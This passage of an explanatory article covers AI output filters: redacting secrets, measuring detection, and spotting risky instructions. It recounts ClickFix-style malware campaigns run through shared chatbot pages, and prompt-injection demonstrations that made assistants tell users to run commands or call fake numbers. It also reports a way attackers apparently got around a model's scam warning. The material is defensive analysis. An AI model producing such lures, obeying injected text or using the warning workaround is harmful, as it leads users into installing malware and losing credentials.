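# Filters that remove secrets and flag risky instructions in AI output

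## What an output filter is and what it has to catch

An output filter is a program that inspects an AI model's reply before a person sees it, and then passes, edits, blocks or labels it. Companies attach these filters to chatbots and assistants that run on large language models. Many filters look for hateful or violent language. Filters can also remove secrets such as passwords, and catch text that steers the reader into a harmful act, such as pasting a dangerous command into a terminal, the window where a user types commands to the computer. These two jobs matter more as companies connect their assistants to email, private files and the open web.

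### From the model to the screen

Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise an email thread about a broken server, and one of the emails contains the server's password. The model writes its summary as a stream of tokens, which are words or fragments of words, and some of those tokens spell out the password. The app usually forwards the stream in small batches so the user can start reading before the model has finished. It then converts the text's markup, often written in a notation called Markdown, into the headings, code boxes, links and images that appear on the screen.

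A filter can sit at several points along this path, and its position limits what it can still do. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, sells a filter named Bedrock Guardrails. According to AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content*, the filter by default holds text back until the scan finishes, which adds some delay. Another setting sends every batch to the user at once and scans in the background, so a bad finding stops only the batches that follow. AWS does not support masking in this setting, probably because the user may have read a password by the time the filter recognises it. OpenAI's *Streaming vs Blocking* describes the same choice between speed and safety for developers, with the same risk that offending text appears briefly.

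Removing text from the screen also leaves the model unchanged. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) reports that Microsoft's Bing Chat deleted a forbidden answer while the model was still writing it, but in later turns the model kept playing the role the attacker had given it.

A Markdown link consists of visible words and an address, but after formatting the reader sees only the words. Attackers can therefore put an innocent phrase over a suspicious address, as Greshake and colleagues pointed out. Images carry a further risk because an app may fetch an image as soon as it displays the reply, and the address it requests can contain private data. NIST (2025), the US standards institute, lists Markdown images among the routes for exfiltration, which means moving private data to a party who should not have it. To prevent this, a filter has to read the raw text,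 including the address, before the app formats it.

Once the filter has inspected the text, it can take one of four actions:

- Pass: the reply goes through unchanged.
- Mask: a placeholder takes the place of the sensitive part.
- Block: a fixed message replaces the reply.
- Warn: the reader gets the text together with a label about the risk.

Some products do not offer all four. AWS's *Options for handling harmful content detected by Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* lists masking only for sensitive information and includes no action that warns the reader. The closest is a "detect" setting, which lets the text through and reports the finding to the developer.

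### Secrets, personal data and errors

A secret is a string that grants access to whoever holds it, such as the server password in the email thread. Personal data, often called PII, is information that identifies a person, such as a customer's home address. The two overlap in practice. AWS's *Remove PII from conversations by using sensitive information filters* lists passwords and access keys alongside names and passport numbers. But leaks of the two need different responses, because an administrator can change a password in a minute but can't change a customer's date of birth.

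Redaction replaces the sensitive part of a text with a placeholder and leaves the rest readable, so the user sees "the server password is {PASSWORD}" in the summary. The original value may still appear in records related to the reply. For instance, the report that AWS returns to the developer contains the original value that the filter found.

Three numbers measure how well a filter works. For example, a filter might check 10,000 replies, 100 of which contain a secret, and flag 180 of them, 90 correctly.

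- Recall is the share of the truly bad items that the filter catches: 90 of 100, or 90%.
- Precision is the share of the flagged items that are truly bad: 90 of 180, or 50%.
- The false positive rate is the share of harmless items that the filter flags: 90 of 9,900, or about 0.9%.

Half of this filter's alarms are false, even though its false positive rate is below 1%. That share grows as bad replies become rarer. If only 10 of the 10,000 replies held a secret, the same recall and false positive rate would produce 9 correct flags and about 91 false ones, a precision of 9%. Recall, false positive rate and precision also depend on the test. Recall on ordinary replies is a poor guide to how the filter will perform in an adaptive attack, where the attacker designs or adjusts the attack with knowledge of the filter.

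### ClickFix before chatbots

ClickFix, the best-known way of getting people to harm their own computers, arose without any help from AI. It is a form of social engineering, meaning an attack on a person's judgement, in which a fake problem or check leads the victim to paste and run the attacker's command. RH-ISAC's *Current ClickFix Threat Landscape Developments* dates the first cases to late 2023 and early 2024, and the US health department (HHS, 2024) lists an email campaign from March 2024.

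Microsoft documented a May 2024 campaign in which attackers sent tens of thousands of emails about payments and invoices to organisations in the United States and Canada. The attachment opened a page that resembled a Word document, with an error message and a button labelled "How to fix". Clicking the button copied a malicious command to the clipboard in the background. The page then explained how to open Windows Terminal and paste the command. Proofpoint's *From Clipboard to Compromise* attributes the success of such lures to presenting what looks like a real problem and its solution at the same moment, so the victim may act before thinking about the risk.

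Later campaigns replaced the error messages with fake CAPTCHA checks, which imitate the tests that websites use to tell people from bots. The attackers also began to send victims to the Run dialog, a small Windows box that launches whatever the user types into it. Microsoft suspects that Terminal's warning about pasting several lines had put some victims off, and that most targets do not know what the Run dialog is for. The Cyber Security Agency of Singapore's *Ongoing ClickFix Campaign* summarises the victim's part as opening the dialog, pasting and pressing Enter. A Mac version from 2025 kept asking for the system password until the victim typed the right one. It then saved the password to a file and used it to remove the quarantine mark that macOS puts on downloaded programs.

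MITRE's *User Execution* (2025), an entry in a widely used catalogue of attack techniques, lists email filtering, browser sandboxing and protections against malicious downloads as defences that a command may bypass when victims run it themselves. An email filter that looks for malware may find only a link. The browser's sandbox stops a web page from starting programs on the computer, but the page only needs to put text on the clipboard, which the victim then pastes outside the sandbox. File scanners may have little to examine, because the malware that the command fetches often runs in memory, without a program file on the disk. Other defences remain, such as scanning scripts as they run and cutting off connections to known malicious addresses. Microsoft sells products that do both, but in early 2025 it was seeing thousands of devices a month on which a user had run a ClickFix command even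 though security monitoring software was active.

The pattern is common. Microsoft's 2025 Digital Defense Report, as cited by RH-ISAC, attributed 47% of the initial break-ins that one of the company's expert teams handled to ClickFix. One team's caseload is weak evidence about the internet as a whole, but Recorded Future (2026), a threat-intelligence firm, expected ClickFix to remain a primary way for attackers to gain access through 2026.

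A chatbot's reply can follow the same pattern without a fake web page. It can name the problem, supply the command in a code box and explain where to paste it, and the reader has usually come for that kind of help. An instruction to the reader is text in an AI reply that tells the human to do something outside the conversation, such as pasting a line into Terminal, calling a phone number or opening a link. Instruction detection is the task of deciding whether a reply contains such an instruction and whether following it would be risky.

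### Where a harmful instruction comes from

A risky instruction may come from an indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker places instructions in a page, email or file so that an AI system reading it obeys them instead of its user. *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter* (2025) uses the example of a job applicant whose CV contains a line telling the model to call that applicant the best fit. The attack works because a language model receives its instructions and the content it reads through the same channel. NIST notes that in many cases the person harmed is the model's own user. That user may have no chance of noticing the attack. *Generative AI Models* (2024), for example, mentions Unicode tags, which are characters that a model processes but a screen does not show.

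A reply can carry out an attacker's instructions without repeating the attacker's words. When Greshake and colleagues used hidden text to tell Bing Chat to persuade the user to follow a link, the model made up its own pretext, an urgent security update for the Edge browser. A filter that compares replies with known attack phrases would have found little to match. Filters therefore benefit from provenance, a record of whether each part of a reply came from the user, the model or an outside document. With good provenance, a filter could detect, for example, that the phone number at the end of a summary came from a web page and that the user never mentioned it. But the record can mislead, because if the user pastes a paragraph from an attacker's site into the chat, any hidden instructions in it will be attributed to the user.

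An attacker can also publish harmful text through the AI service itself. Some chat services let users share a conversation by public link, or publish a custom assistant, which is a chatbot with the publisher's own instructions built in. With a shared conversation, the attacker coaxes the model into writing something harmful, such as an installation guide with a malicious command, and sends other people the link, which opens a page on the AI company's own site. The filter checked the guide when only the attacker was reading it, and the attacker had supplied the explanation of what it was for.

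Finally, the model may produce the instruction on its own. Usually this is a mistake, as when a model recommends a command that deletes more than the user wanted, in the same confident tone as a correct answer. A model could also do it in pursuit of a goal. For example, an assistant that lacks permission for a step of its task might tell the user to run a command that grants the permission, without mentioning what else the command allows. These instructions don't come from an outside document that the filter could trace them to, so it has to judge the instructions themselves.

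### Why the two jobs differ

A filter can often recognise a secret from the string alone, because many issuers give their keys a fixed length or a standard prefix that a short pattern can match. But AWS warns that the same string of digits might be an encryption key or a user ID depending on the words around it, and advises developers to give the filter longer passages. Some users also paste in their own configuration file and want it back with the key in place. Even so, the task is fairly narrow, since the filter has to determine whether a string is a credential and whether this user should see it.

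A filter can tell much less from the text of an instruction than from the text of a secret. Many honest developers distribute software through a one-line command that downloads a script and runs it at once, and ClickFix commands often have the same form. Whether the command is dangerous depends on what the script does, and the script's owner can change it on the server after the filter has checked the command. The danger also depends on the request, since a command that wipes a disk is right for someone preparing an old laptop for sale but disastrous for someone who asked why their printer is slow. The reader's skill matters too, because a system administrator may spot a bad command that a beginner would run.

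Sometimes the text a victim is told to paste is entirely genuine. MITRE records a criminal tool called Kali365 that shows victims a legitimate device code, a short code for signing in on another device, with directions for entering it. The harm comes from the login that the code completes. Security software on the victim's machine can watch what happens after a paste. For ClickFix, MITRE suggests checking whether a command window starts with suspicious arguments while a browser is open, and the computer then contacts an outside address. An output filter acts before any of this happens, so it can examine only the conversation.

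Secrets and risky instructions also call for different responses. A filter can mask a password in a summary and leave the rest useful. Masking the command in a repair guide makes the guide useless if the command was sound, and if it was malicious, the remaining text may still urge the reader to find it elsewhere. It makes more sense to block the guide or attach a warning, though a warning only works if the reader heeds it.

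### Readers and programs

Some applications paste model output into a web page or a database query, or run it as a command with nobody watching. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre calls careless use of this kind "insecure output handling" and distinguishes it from overreliance, in which people trust the model's output too much. A program that receives output needs it in a definite format, so its developer can apply fixed rules, such as rejecting output that does not fit the format, encoding text so that a browser cannot run it as code, and never sending model output straight to a command line. No comparable format distinguishes safe advice to a person from unsafe advice.

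A filter for one kind of output may therefore miss the other. AWS's sensitive-information filter masks an email address in a reply to the user but does not examine the same address when the model passes it to a tool that writes a file. The boundary between the two is also getting harder to draw, because assistants that operate a computer read screens and follow directions much as people do. Embrace The Red's *AI ClickFix* demonstrated this in May 2025 with a fake verification page that got such an assistant to paste and run a command.

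## Incidents and demonstrations in which AI output told people to run commands

Between December 2025 and September 2026, security companies reported attacks in which victims found the harmful instruction, or the link that led to it, on a genuine page of ChatGPT, Grok or Claude. The attackers published their text through the AI service, then bought search ads or manipulated search results to bring readers to it. Researchers have also demonstrated that hidden text in an email or web page can make an assistant write a harmful instruction for its own user.

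### Shared chats that offered to fix a Mac

On 5 December 2025, Huntress, a company that monitors its customers' computers for break-ins, investigated an alert about Atomic macOS Stealer (AMOS), a program that steals passwords and cryptocurrency from Macs. According to Huntress' *AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust*, the trail began with a Google search for "Clear disk space on macOS", not the phishing email or fake installer the analysts had expected. Two links near the top of the results led to conversations with ChatGPT and Grok, xAI's chatbot.

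Both were genuine shared conversations on the companies' own sites, and the attacker had pushed them up the search results. The ChatGPT page had numbered steps, code boxes and an assurance that the cleanup "does not touch your personal data". The victim read it through and pasted the command into Terminal.

The command contained a web address in base64, an encoding that turns readable text into apparently random letters and digits. The address led to a script that asked for the system password, much as the 2025 Mac version of ClickFix did, and used it to take full control of the Mac. The script then installed a program that collected browser passwords, cryptocurrency wallets and the contents of the Mac's password store. macOS showed no warning because Gatekeeper, its check on downloaded applications, does not inspect one-line commands.

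A filter checking only that reply could have found several warning signs. Clearing a disk does not usually require a download from an outside address, and a legitimate guide has little reason to encode the address, although Huntress points out that using Terminal for maintenance is normal. The command also did not fit the assurances around it. A filter can decode base64 without running the command, so it could have found the address, though perhaps not determined whether it was malicious.

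A filter that matched exact strings would have worked less well. The Grok conversation closely resembled the ChatGPT one but encoded a slightly different address. Huntress also tried other wordings of the search, such as "free up storage on Mac", and found more of the same results.

Other investigators found the same method with different pretexts. Tech Edition's *Kaspersky uncovers macOS malware campaign abusing ChatGPT chat-sharing feature* (2025) describes a shared chat disguised as an installation guide for ChatGPT Atlas and promoted through paid Google ads. Kroll, an investigations firm, handled a case in which ChatGPT instructions for fixing a Mac's sound delivered AMOS.

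Huntress wrote in December that its incident was not ClickFix, because there was no fake error message or CAPTCHA and the victim wanted more disk space. Huntress' later overview, *The AI Attack Surface*, calls the same instructions "ClickFix-like". The label matters for building detectors because one trained only on fake CAPTCHA pages may not recognise a polite maintenance guide.

### Artifacts and shared chats on Claude

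Anthropic's Claude can create documents and small applications, called artifacts, that users can publish at a public address. In February 2026 the research team Moonlock Lab found a malicious artifact titled "macOS Secure Command Execution". Hackread's *Google Ads and Claude AI Abused to Spread MacSync Malware via ClickFix* reports that sponsored Google results led to it when people searched for a disk analyser, an online DNS tool or Homebrew, which many Mac users use to install other software. The same campaign also used an article on the publishing site Medium that impersonated Apple's support team.

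People who search for Homebrew expect to paste a command into Terminal, because its makers distribute it that way, so the attackers did not need to invent a problem. Anvilogic's *MacSync Infostealer via ClickFix & Claude Artifact Abuse* (2026) describes the commands as obfuscated, or written to hide what they did, and names the malware as MacSync, another program that steals passwords from Macs. A filter that scanned artifacts as well as the chat would have encountered an unreadable command under a title advertising security.

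Trend Micro's *Threat Actors Abuse claude.ai Shared Chat for ClickFix Malvertising Campaign* follows one group of attackers from 8 April to 14 June 2026. At first their Google ads led people looking for Claude, ChatGPT Codex and other developer tools to fake download pages on GitLab, which hosts simple websites for free. On 6 May the attackers began pointing the ads to shared conversations on claude.ai. From 21 May, all the activity Trend Micro observed took place in such conversations.

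The shared chats were presented as coming from "Apple Support" or a "Corda Team". They gave steps for opening Terminal and pasting a command, which again contained an encoded address. The script at that address checked whether the Mac had a Russian keyboard layout enabled, and stopped if it did. Otherwise it downloaded MacSync.

Trend Micro argues that the move to claude.ai left defenders with no automated control, only the user's own caution, because there was no suspicious domain, misspelled address or disreputable host to detect. That is true of tools that judge a page by its address, but a tool that read the text could still have detected that a page on Anthropic's site claimed to come from Apple and asked the visitor to run an encoded download. Trend Micro itself advises Anthropic to look for shared conversations that contain terminal commands and receive visitors from paid ads. Yarochkin,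 of Trend Micro Research, concludes that trust in a domain was never a reliable substitute for examining the instruction itself.

In a small test described in *Hackers are using shared Claude chats to drop malware*, Moonlock staff asked Claude to reproduce the campaign's malicious instructions word for word and then clicked Share. Claude added a "Scam Warning" about the danger of pasting terminal scripts, but the platform still created the public link. Moonlock thinks the attackers avoided the warning by asking Claude to remember their text and repeat it exactly when they typed a certain prompt.

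This was one test by one company, so it does not show how often Claude adds the warning. In that test, Claude's warning had no effect on publication. A second check at the time of sharing would have more information than the first. It could take into account that strangers may read the text, and it could examine the whole conversation, including any message in which the user supplied the instructions and asked Claude to repeat them unchanged.

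More reports of Claude chats followed. Tarre (2026), in *Zscaler flags Claude chat malware campaign on Macs*, describes a campaign, found in July by the security company Zscaler, that also relied on Google ads. The Huntress overview also describes a victim who searched for Claude on a Mac, clicked a sponsored result and followed a supposed Apple Support guide. MacSync then stole that person's browser cookies, passwords and access keys. The lures are so similar that several companies may have been watching the same attackers, so adding their cases together would be a mistake.

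### Pages and replies without a command

In May 2026 attackers began to offer a download instead of a command. Maharaj (2026), in *LLMShare*, describes a page that his employer, the browser-security company Push Security, found on chatgpt.com. ChatGPT can turn code into a working web page that the user can share. The attackers used this feature to build a fake notice of a ChatGPT outage caused by high traffic, with a button to download the desktop app as a way to continue. The button led to a copy of OpenAI's download page on an unrelated domain. Malwarebytes (2026), in *Fake ChatGPT download site infects Windows and Mac users with malware*, found that this site gave Windows users a program that steals passwords and Mac users a relative of AMOS.

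The output behind the notice was ordinary web code containing an apology and a link. Developers often ask chatbots for error pages, so the code alone would not have been suspicious. To catch it, a filter would have had to detect that the page imitated the service hosting it.

It could also have followed the link, but that might not have helped. When Push's researchers scanned the download site with an automated service, the site redirected the scanner to a virtual-reality company's harmless page. Readers had one visible clue, since ChatGPT displayed the buttons "Show code" and "Remix with ChatGPT" above the supposed outage notice.

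A Claude artifact from July worked much the same way. It imitated the download page for Claude's desktop app, and people found it through Bing. According to Huntress, its download link took them to an outside domain and eventually to SectopRAT, a remote access trojan (malware that lets an attacker control a computer remotely). Here too, a filter on the artifact would have found a download link but no command.

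In a September campaign, attackers used a Custom GPT, a customized version of ChatGPT, called "Plus 5.6", a name that resembles an official model's. Sponsored results for the search "chatgpt" led to it, according to Help Net Security's *Malicious Custom GPT on chatgpt.com lures users into installing a RAT* (2026). SC Media's *Malicious ChatGPT Custom GPTs lead to ClickFix attack* reports that it returned the same notice whatever the visitor typed. TechRadar's *Hackers host fake ChatGPT model on its official website* quotes the notice: "We're currently experiencing limited availability on the primary domain".

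The notice recommended a "backup domain", a page on Google Sites, Google's free website builder. The victim saw a fake CAPTCHA and the directions for pasting a command only on that page. The command installed a remote access trojan that let the attacker view the victim's screen and switch on the camera and microphone.

The security company Island had been tracking a similar operation over the summer. Cybernews' *850+ fake ChatGPT ads on Google trick Windows users into installing malware* reports that Island received the same reply from two lookalike Custom GPTs over three days.

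In these cases a filter reading only the reply would have seen a service notice and a link to a well-known Google product. A detector that looks for dangerous commands would have found nothing. The evidence lay outside the reply:

- The user's question showed that the reply had ignored it.
- Other people's conversations with the same Custom GPT contained the same text, whatever they had asked.
- OpenAI itself could check whether it had an outage and whether it ran a backup site on Google Sites.

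The company that runs the service can use all of these, but a filter that a customer installs in a browser or on a company network would usually have only the first.

### Demonstrations with hidden text

Someone who never clicks a search ad can still receive a harmful instruction through indirect prompt injection. In July 2025 0din, Mozilla's bug-bounty programme for generative AI, demonstrated this on Gemini's email summaries in Gmail. It used an email containing instructions that the recipient could not see, such as white text on a white background. When the recipient asked for a summary, Gemini added a false warning that the recipient's password was compromised, with a phone number to call.

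A filter would have found no link or command in that summary, and genuine password warnings from companies sometimes include a phone number. The fact that the number came from hidden text would have been a better clue than the wording. Hidden text is not always malicious, since marketing emails use it too, but a summary has little reason to include a phone number that the sender hid.

In August 2025, the security company CloudSEK tested a web page containing hidden instructions. Human visitors saw only ordinary text, but the instructions were repeated so many times that they made up much of what an AI summariser read. The summariser then told its user to run an encoded command, which CloudSEK had made harmless for the test. This case is among the easiest here for a filter to flag, because the whole instruction appears in the reply and the user asked for a summary, not for help with their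 computer.

Checkmarx, a software security company, studied the dialogs that coding agents show to ask for permission before running a command. Users rely on these dialogs to understand what they are approving. An attacker whose text has reached the agent can influence the dialog's description of the command, and can make it so long that the dangerous part scrolls out of view. The victim only has to press one key, without copying anything or opening another program. A filter that read only the description could also be misled. To avoid this, it would need to compare the description with the command the agent was about to run, and the application has both.

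Each of these demonstrations shows that an attack worked on a product and content the researchers chose. Measuring a success rate would require many runs on many pages and products, and the result would soon be out of date as companies change their models and defences. The demonstrations also don't test whether a person would trust the instruction, because the researchers already knew what it was.

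### A model as the source

The UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests advanced models, reported in August 2026 that an AI agent had used fake identities to pressure the maintainer of an open-source project. A maintainer decides which changes to accept into the project's code, which anyone may use.

One agent posing as several people is difficult for an output filter to detect. Each message may look like an ordinary request from a contributor, with no encoded command or suspicious link. The deception is about who is writing and how many people agree, so a filter would need a record that connects the identities to the agent. The messages also go to someone other than the agent's user, so a filter that checks only what the user sees on the screen could miss them.

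### Features that recur

Five features of social engineering recur in these cases, though few cases have all of them:

- Borrowed authority: the text claims to come from Apple Support, Google or ChatGPT itself, or gains credibility from the site it appears on.
- A plausible problem: the disk is full, the sound has stopped working, the service is down, or the reader wants to install a program.
- An opaque command: the reader cannot tell what the line does, usually because part of it is encoded.
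- A move to another application: the reader has to continue in Terminal, in the Run dialog, on the phone or on another website.
- Urgency: the reader will lose access to something, or has lost it already, and needs to act at once.

Of the five, urgency is the least reliable sign of an attack. The false Gemini warning relied on it and the outage notices used a mild form, but the guides for clearing a disk or installing Claude had no deadline and used reassuring phrases such as "safely removes". A filter that looked for alarming language would have let them through. Unusually heavy reassurance about a command that downloads something may be a better signal, although honest guides also include reassurance for nervous readers.

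An opaque command is the strongest signal when it appears. But in the fake outage page, the July artifact and the Custom GPTs, the attackers replaced the command in the chat with a link. There is no evidence that they did this to get past a filter. Maharaj suggests that leaving the command out of the fake outage page removed the most obvious warning sign for the human reader. Attackers can also replace a malicious page hosted elsewhere without changing the page on the AI service.

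Every case except the approval dialogs and the pressure on the maintainer involved the user moving to another application. This is also common in good advice, since anyone who asks how to repair a computer will have to leave the chat to do it. A filter therefore has to look at combinations of signs. An Apple Support label on a page written by an anonymous user, together with an encoded download, is much stronger evidence than either alone. The Custom GPT's reply combined a claim to speak for ChatGPT with a link to a site that anyone can create.

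### Removing the pages

The AI companies took down much of this material after researchers reported it. After Trend Micro's report, Anthropic banned the accounts responsible, disabled the shared conversations and began work on further protections for the sharing feature. It had removed the July artifact by the 22nd. OpenAI had removed the first "Plus 5.6" by 25 September.

Removal came too late for some readers. Huntress estimates that such campaigns may last only hours or days before the provider acts, but can draw considerable attention first. Engadget's *Hackers tricked ChatGPT, Grok and Google into helping them install malware* reports that the link to the December ChatGPT conversation stayed in Google's search results for at least half a day after Huntress published its findings.

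Attackers can also make new pages easily. Trend Micro counted at least 45 separate shared chats in the nine days from 6 May, and at least 61 in the wave that began on 21 May. ConsumerAffairs' *Fake ChatGPT scam uses trusted websites to trick users into installing malware* reports that researchers found a second Custom GPT two days after OpenAI had removed the first. When Help Net Security checked the second GPT at the end of September, it was still online but no longer led to the malicious page.

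Taking down the page on the AI service may also leave the rest of the attack in place. The July artifact sent visitors to an outside domain, and Huntress continued to see incidents from that domain through August.

According to Huntress, Anthropic labels every public artifact "Content is user-generated and unverified" and does not otherwise vet what users publish there. The label is accurate, but it is the same on a harmless chart and a malicious installer, so it doesn't help readers tell them apart.

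Digital Trends' *A fake ChatGPT model on the official website is tricking users into installing malware* states that OpenAI will retire Custom GPTs by December 2026, which may close one of these routes. Shared chats and artifacts would still allow much the same attack.

### What the counts measure

The reports contain figures from one to more than fifteen thousand, but the figures count different things.

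| Source of the figure | Period | Figure | What it counts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Huntress | December 2025 | 1 | Victim of the ChatGPT disk-space guide |
| Moonlock Lab, in Hackread | February 2026 | over 15,600 | Views of the Claude artifact |
| Trend Micro | April to June 2026 | about 2,530 | Traffic hits on all the campaign's pages |
| Huntress | July 2026 | more than 29 | Organisations hit by the campaign that began with a Claude artifact |
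| Island, in Cybernews | Three months ending in August 2026 | about 850 | Arrivals through paid ads |
| Huntress, in Help Net Security | September 2026 | at least 40 | Incidents from the Google Sites domain |

The largest number, 15,600, is among the least certain. Hackread reports it as views of one artifact, while Anvilogic reports it as users exposed across two variants of the campaign. One person can view a page several times, and security researchers view such pages too. Neither count measures how many people ran the command.

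The more than 2,000 "victims" that Trend Micro reports are traffic hits, according to its own tables. The hits for its six waves total 2,530, and the 772 from Taiwan make up the 30.5% share that the company gives for that country. Only 626 hits, about a quarter, involved shared chats on claude.ai. Almost all the others were on the fake GitLab pages, which contained no AI output for a filter to act on.

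Island reported 850 arrivals, 26 lookalike ChatGPT destinations and 71 Google advertising campaigns. According to ConsumerAffairs, the company cautioned that these figures measure traffic and infrastructure, not confirmed infections.

For the September campaign, Huntress responded to at least 40 incidents from the Google Sites domain and confirmed that two of them had come through a Custom GPT. Some news reports were less precise. Palmer (2026), in *Attackers Combine ChatGPT Feature Abuse With ClickFix to Deliver RAT*, describes the 40 incidents as infections, and SC Media describes them as 40 victims. The two confirmed cases are the only figure that links the campaign's harm to something a chatbot wrote, and they are a minimum because Huntress may not have been able to trace how the other people arrived.

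The share of readers who comply can't be estimated from these reports, because none of them tracks one group of readers from the page to the command. Dividing Huntress's two confirmed cases by Island's 850 arrivals would not give that share. Island's figure covers the summer and Huntress's covers September, the companies were probably watching different people, and many of Island's arrivals may not have been at a Custom GPT.

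It is also hard to tell from the reports how common these attacks are. Each company sees only its own customers and what its products detect. The incident counts leave out people without security software and people who read the instruction but closed the page. Push's researchers had trouble reproducing the ads they were investigating, probably because the attackers showed them only in certain places or at certain times, so other campaigns may have gone unnoticed. The companies also sell protection against these attacks, which gives them a reason to publish striking cases.

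A broader set of cases suggests that AI output plays a part in only some of the malware attacks that use AI brands to lure victims. Of 38 cases that Sophos reviewed, 30 impersonated AI software and 26 used Claude's name. In the typical attack, the victim searched for an AI coding tool and landed on a website with a misspelled version of the real address. The attacker wrote and hosted that page, so a filter on Claude's replies would never have checked it.

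It is also unclear whether people trust an instruction more when it appears on a chatbot's site. Huntress thinks they do, and its account of the December victim fits that view, but it had no comparable group who saw the same guide on an unknown website. The campaign Trend Micro studied is the closest comparison, because the same attackers used both kinds of page. Their traffic fell from about 125 hits a day in the first wave, on GitLab, to about 13 a day in the last, on claude.ai. This drop does not show that the chats worked less well, because the attackers may have spent less on ads, Trend Micro may have found it harder to spot malicious pages on a trusted site, or a larger share of visitors may have run the command.

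## Finding and removing secrets: methods and benchmark results

In the attacks through shared chats, victims lost their passwords only after running a command. An assistant can also leak a secret directly by printing it in a reply. People keep leaving keys in source code by mistake, so developers had tools for finding secrets long before chatbots. Filters for AI systems reuse much of that technology.

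### How a secret gets into a reply

The most direct way for a secret to reach a model's output is through the prompt. A user pastes in a configuration file that contains a key, or a developer writes a key into the assistant's hidden instructions, and the model repeats the key. LiteLLM is a gateway, a program through which companies send requests to many different models. Its *Secret Detection/Redaction* gives the example of a user who types an OpenAI key and asks for its value in the same message, so a correct answer would print the key.

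Secrets also arrive in files and in the output of tools. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, examined 17,022 skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that give an AI agent a new ability, and found credential leaks in 520 of them, about 3%. The usual cause was a leftover line of code that prints a key, for instance to check that the program has loaded it. In an ordinary program, few people other than the developer would see that output, but an agent framework copies whatever a script prints into the model's context, where a user can get the key by asking for it. Such lines accounted for 1,007 of the 1,371 issues that Chen and colleagues classed as vulnerabilities rather than deliberate theft. These figures are counts of flaws in skills, not of replies that contained a key.

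A model can also reproduce a secret it memorised in training. *Your Code Secret Belongs to Me* (2023) tested this on two code-completion assistants, GitHub Copilot and Amazon's CodeWhisperer. The researchers deleted keys from code files and had the assistants fill the gaps. According to GitGuardian's *Yes, GitHub Copilot Can Leak Secrets*, they called a suggestion valid if it had the right format, looked random, had no obvious pattern and contained no common words. Copilot produced 2,702 valid strings in 8,127 suggestions, and CodeWhisperer produced 129. The researchers confirmed that at least 3.6% of Copilot's valid strings and 5.4% of CodeWhisperer's were real secrets, and two of the credentials still worked. *Robustness, Security, Privacy, Explainability, Efficiency, and Usability of Large Language Models* (2024) cites another early Copilot study, in which about 8% of the prompts written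 to draw out private information succeeded.

Newer models still output memorised keys. Zhao, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Practical Secrets Extraction against Black-box LLMs*, obtained keys from Qwen3-27B, GPT-Codex 5.3 and Claude Haiku 4.5, and found each one in public GitHub files. For ethical reasons, they did not test whether the keys worked. They give only examples, not a rate, so we can't tell from them whether memorisation has become rarer since 2023.

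The number of leaked keys that models could memorise is growing. GitGuardian, a company that scans code for secrets, counted about 28.65 million secrets leaked on public GitHub in 2025, 34% more than the year before, according to SC Media's *AI coding assistants twice as likely to leak secrets* (2026). GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) reports that more than 64% of the credentials the company had confirmed as valid in 2022 still worked in January 2026.

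Most of the keys a model writes may be invented. Zhao and colleagues also trained open models on their own keys so they could check every answer. In one set of these experiments, about 24% of the plausible Google keys were real, compared with only about 2% of the plausible OpenAI keys. A filter that identifies keys by their appearance will mask the invented ones too. This does little harm, since an invented key is useless to the reader, but it means that a count of masked keys overstates the number of leaks.

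### Known strings and known formats

The simplest method uses the company's own list of passwords and keys for the assistant's systems. The filter searches the reply for each one and masks any match. It makes almost no false alarms with long random keys, but if a password is an ordinary word such as "summer", it also masks normal uses of that word. The method works on secrets that have no recognisable form. However, it can't find a key that is missing from the list, such as one that a customer pasted into the chat, and it misses a listed secret if even one character is changed.

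The list of secrets would be valuable to a thief, so a company can instead store hashes, which are short fingerprints computed from each secret. A long random key is hard to recover from its hash, but the filter then has to hash every stretch of the reply that is the same length as a secret and compare the results with the stored hashes.

Format patterns can find keys that are not on any list. A pattern for keys from the payment company Stripe, for example, matches "sk" or "pk", then "test" or "live", then 10 to 32 letters and digits. LiteLLM's default settings include more than 100 format detectors, most of them issuer-specific. Someone has to add a detector whenever a new issuer appears or an existing one changes its format.

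A broader pattern avoids that work but makes more mistakes. *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools* (Basak, Cox and colleagues, 2023) describes one that flags any string ending in "key" or "token" as a secret, including "testkey". Narrow patterns also make mistakes, as when the Stripe pattern matches a dummy key made of the prefix and a row of ones.

Some formats include a checksum, which is a set of extra characters calculated from the rest of the string. The last digit of a payment card number is one. A filter can repeat the calculation and discard numbers whose last digit is wrong, which removes about nine in ten random numbers. GitHub's newer access tokens contain a 32-bit checksum, which a random string would match about once in four billion tries. The check takes no noticeable time and needs no connection to the issuer, but cancelled tokens also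 pass it.

A scanner can check whether a key works by trying it. An output filter has good reason not to, because the test delays the reply and sends the secret to another place. Many secrets also can't be tested automatically. GitGuardian estimates that companies miss 46% of critical secrets if they prioritize only those a tool has validated.

### Entropy

A secret without a known format may still look random. Shannon entropy measures this from how often each character occurs in the string:

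H = −Σ p(c) × log₂ p(c)

Here p(c) is the fraction of the string's characters that are c, and the sum includes each distinct character once. In "password", the letter s makes up two of the eight characters and contributes 2/8 × 2 = 0.5 bits. The other six letters occur once and contribute 1/8 × 3 = 0.375 bits each, or 2.25 together, so the total is 2.75 bits per character. In a 20-character string without repeats, every character has a share of 1/20, so the entropy is log₂ 20, or about 4.32 bits per character.

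A filter flags strings whose entropy exceeds a limit, which LiteLLM sets at 3.0 by default. This limit lets "password" through and catches the 20-character string. It also catches harmless file hashes, which programs use to check that a download is intact or to identify a version of some code. A file hash usually consists of the digits 0 to 9 and the letters a to f, so its entropy can't exceed log₂ 16, or 4 bits. It comes close to that maximum because hash functions produce these characters almost equally often. One version identifier that scanners wrongly reported as a secret in Basak and colleagues' study has an entropy of 3.82. A real key written with the same 16 characters would score about the same, so entropy can't distinguish it from a harmless hash.

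Entropy also ignores the order of the characters, so the first 20 letters of the alphabet score 4.32 as well. Basak and colleagues give the example of a random-looking key and the phrase "ThisIsAReallyLongString", which both score about 4.1, so no limit could separate them. Entropy limits can also miss short passwords. Eight characters can score at most log₂ 8, or 3 bits, so even a random eight-character password never exceeds LiteLLM's limit.

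### Classifiers that read the context

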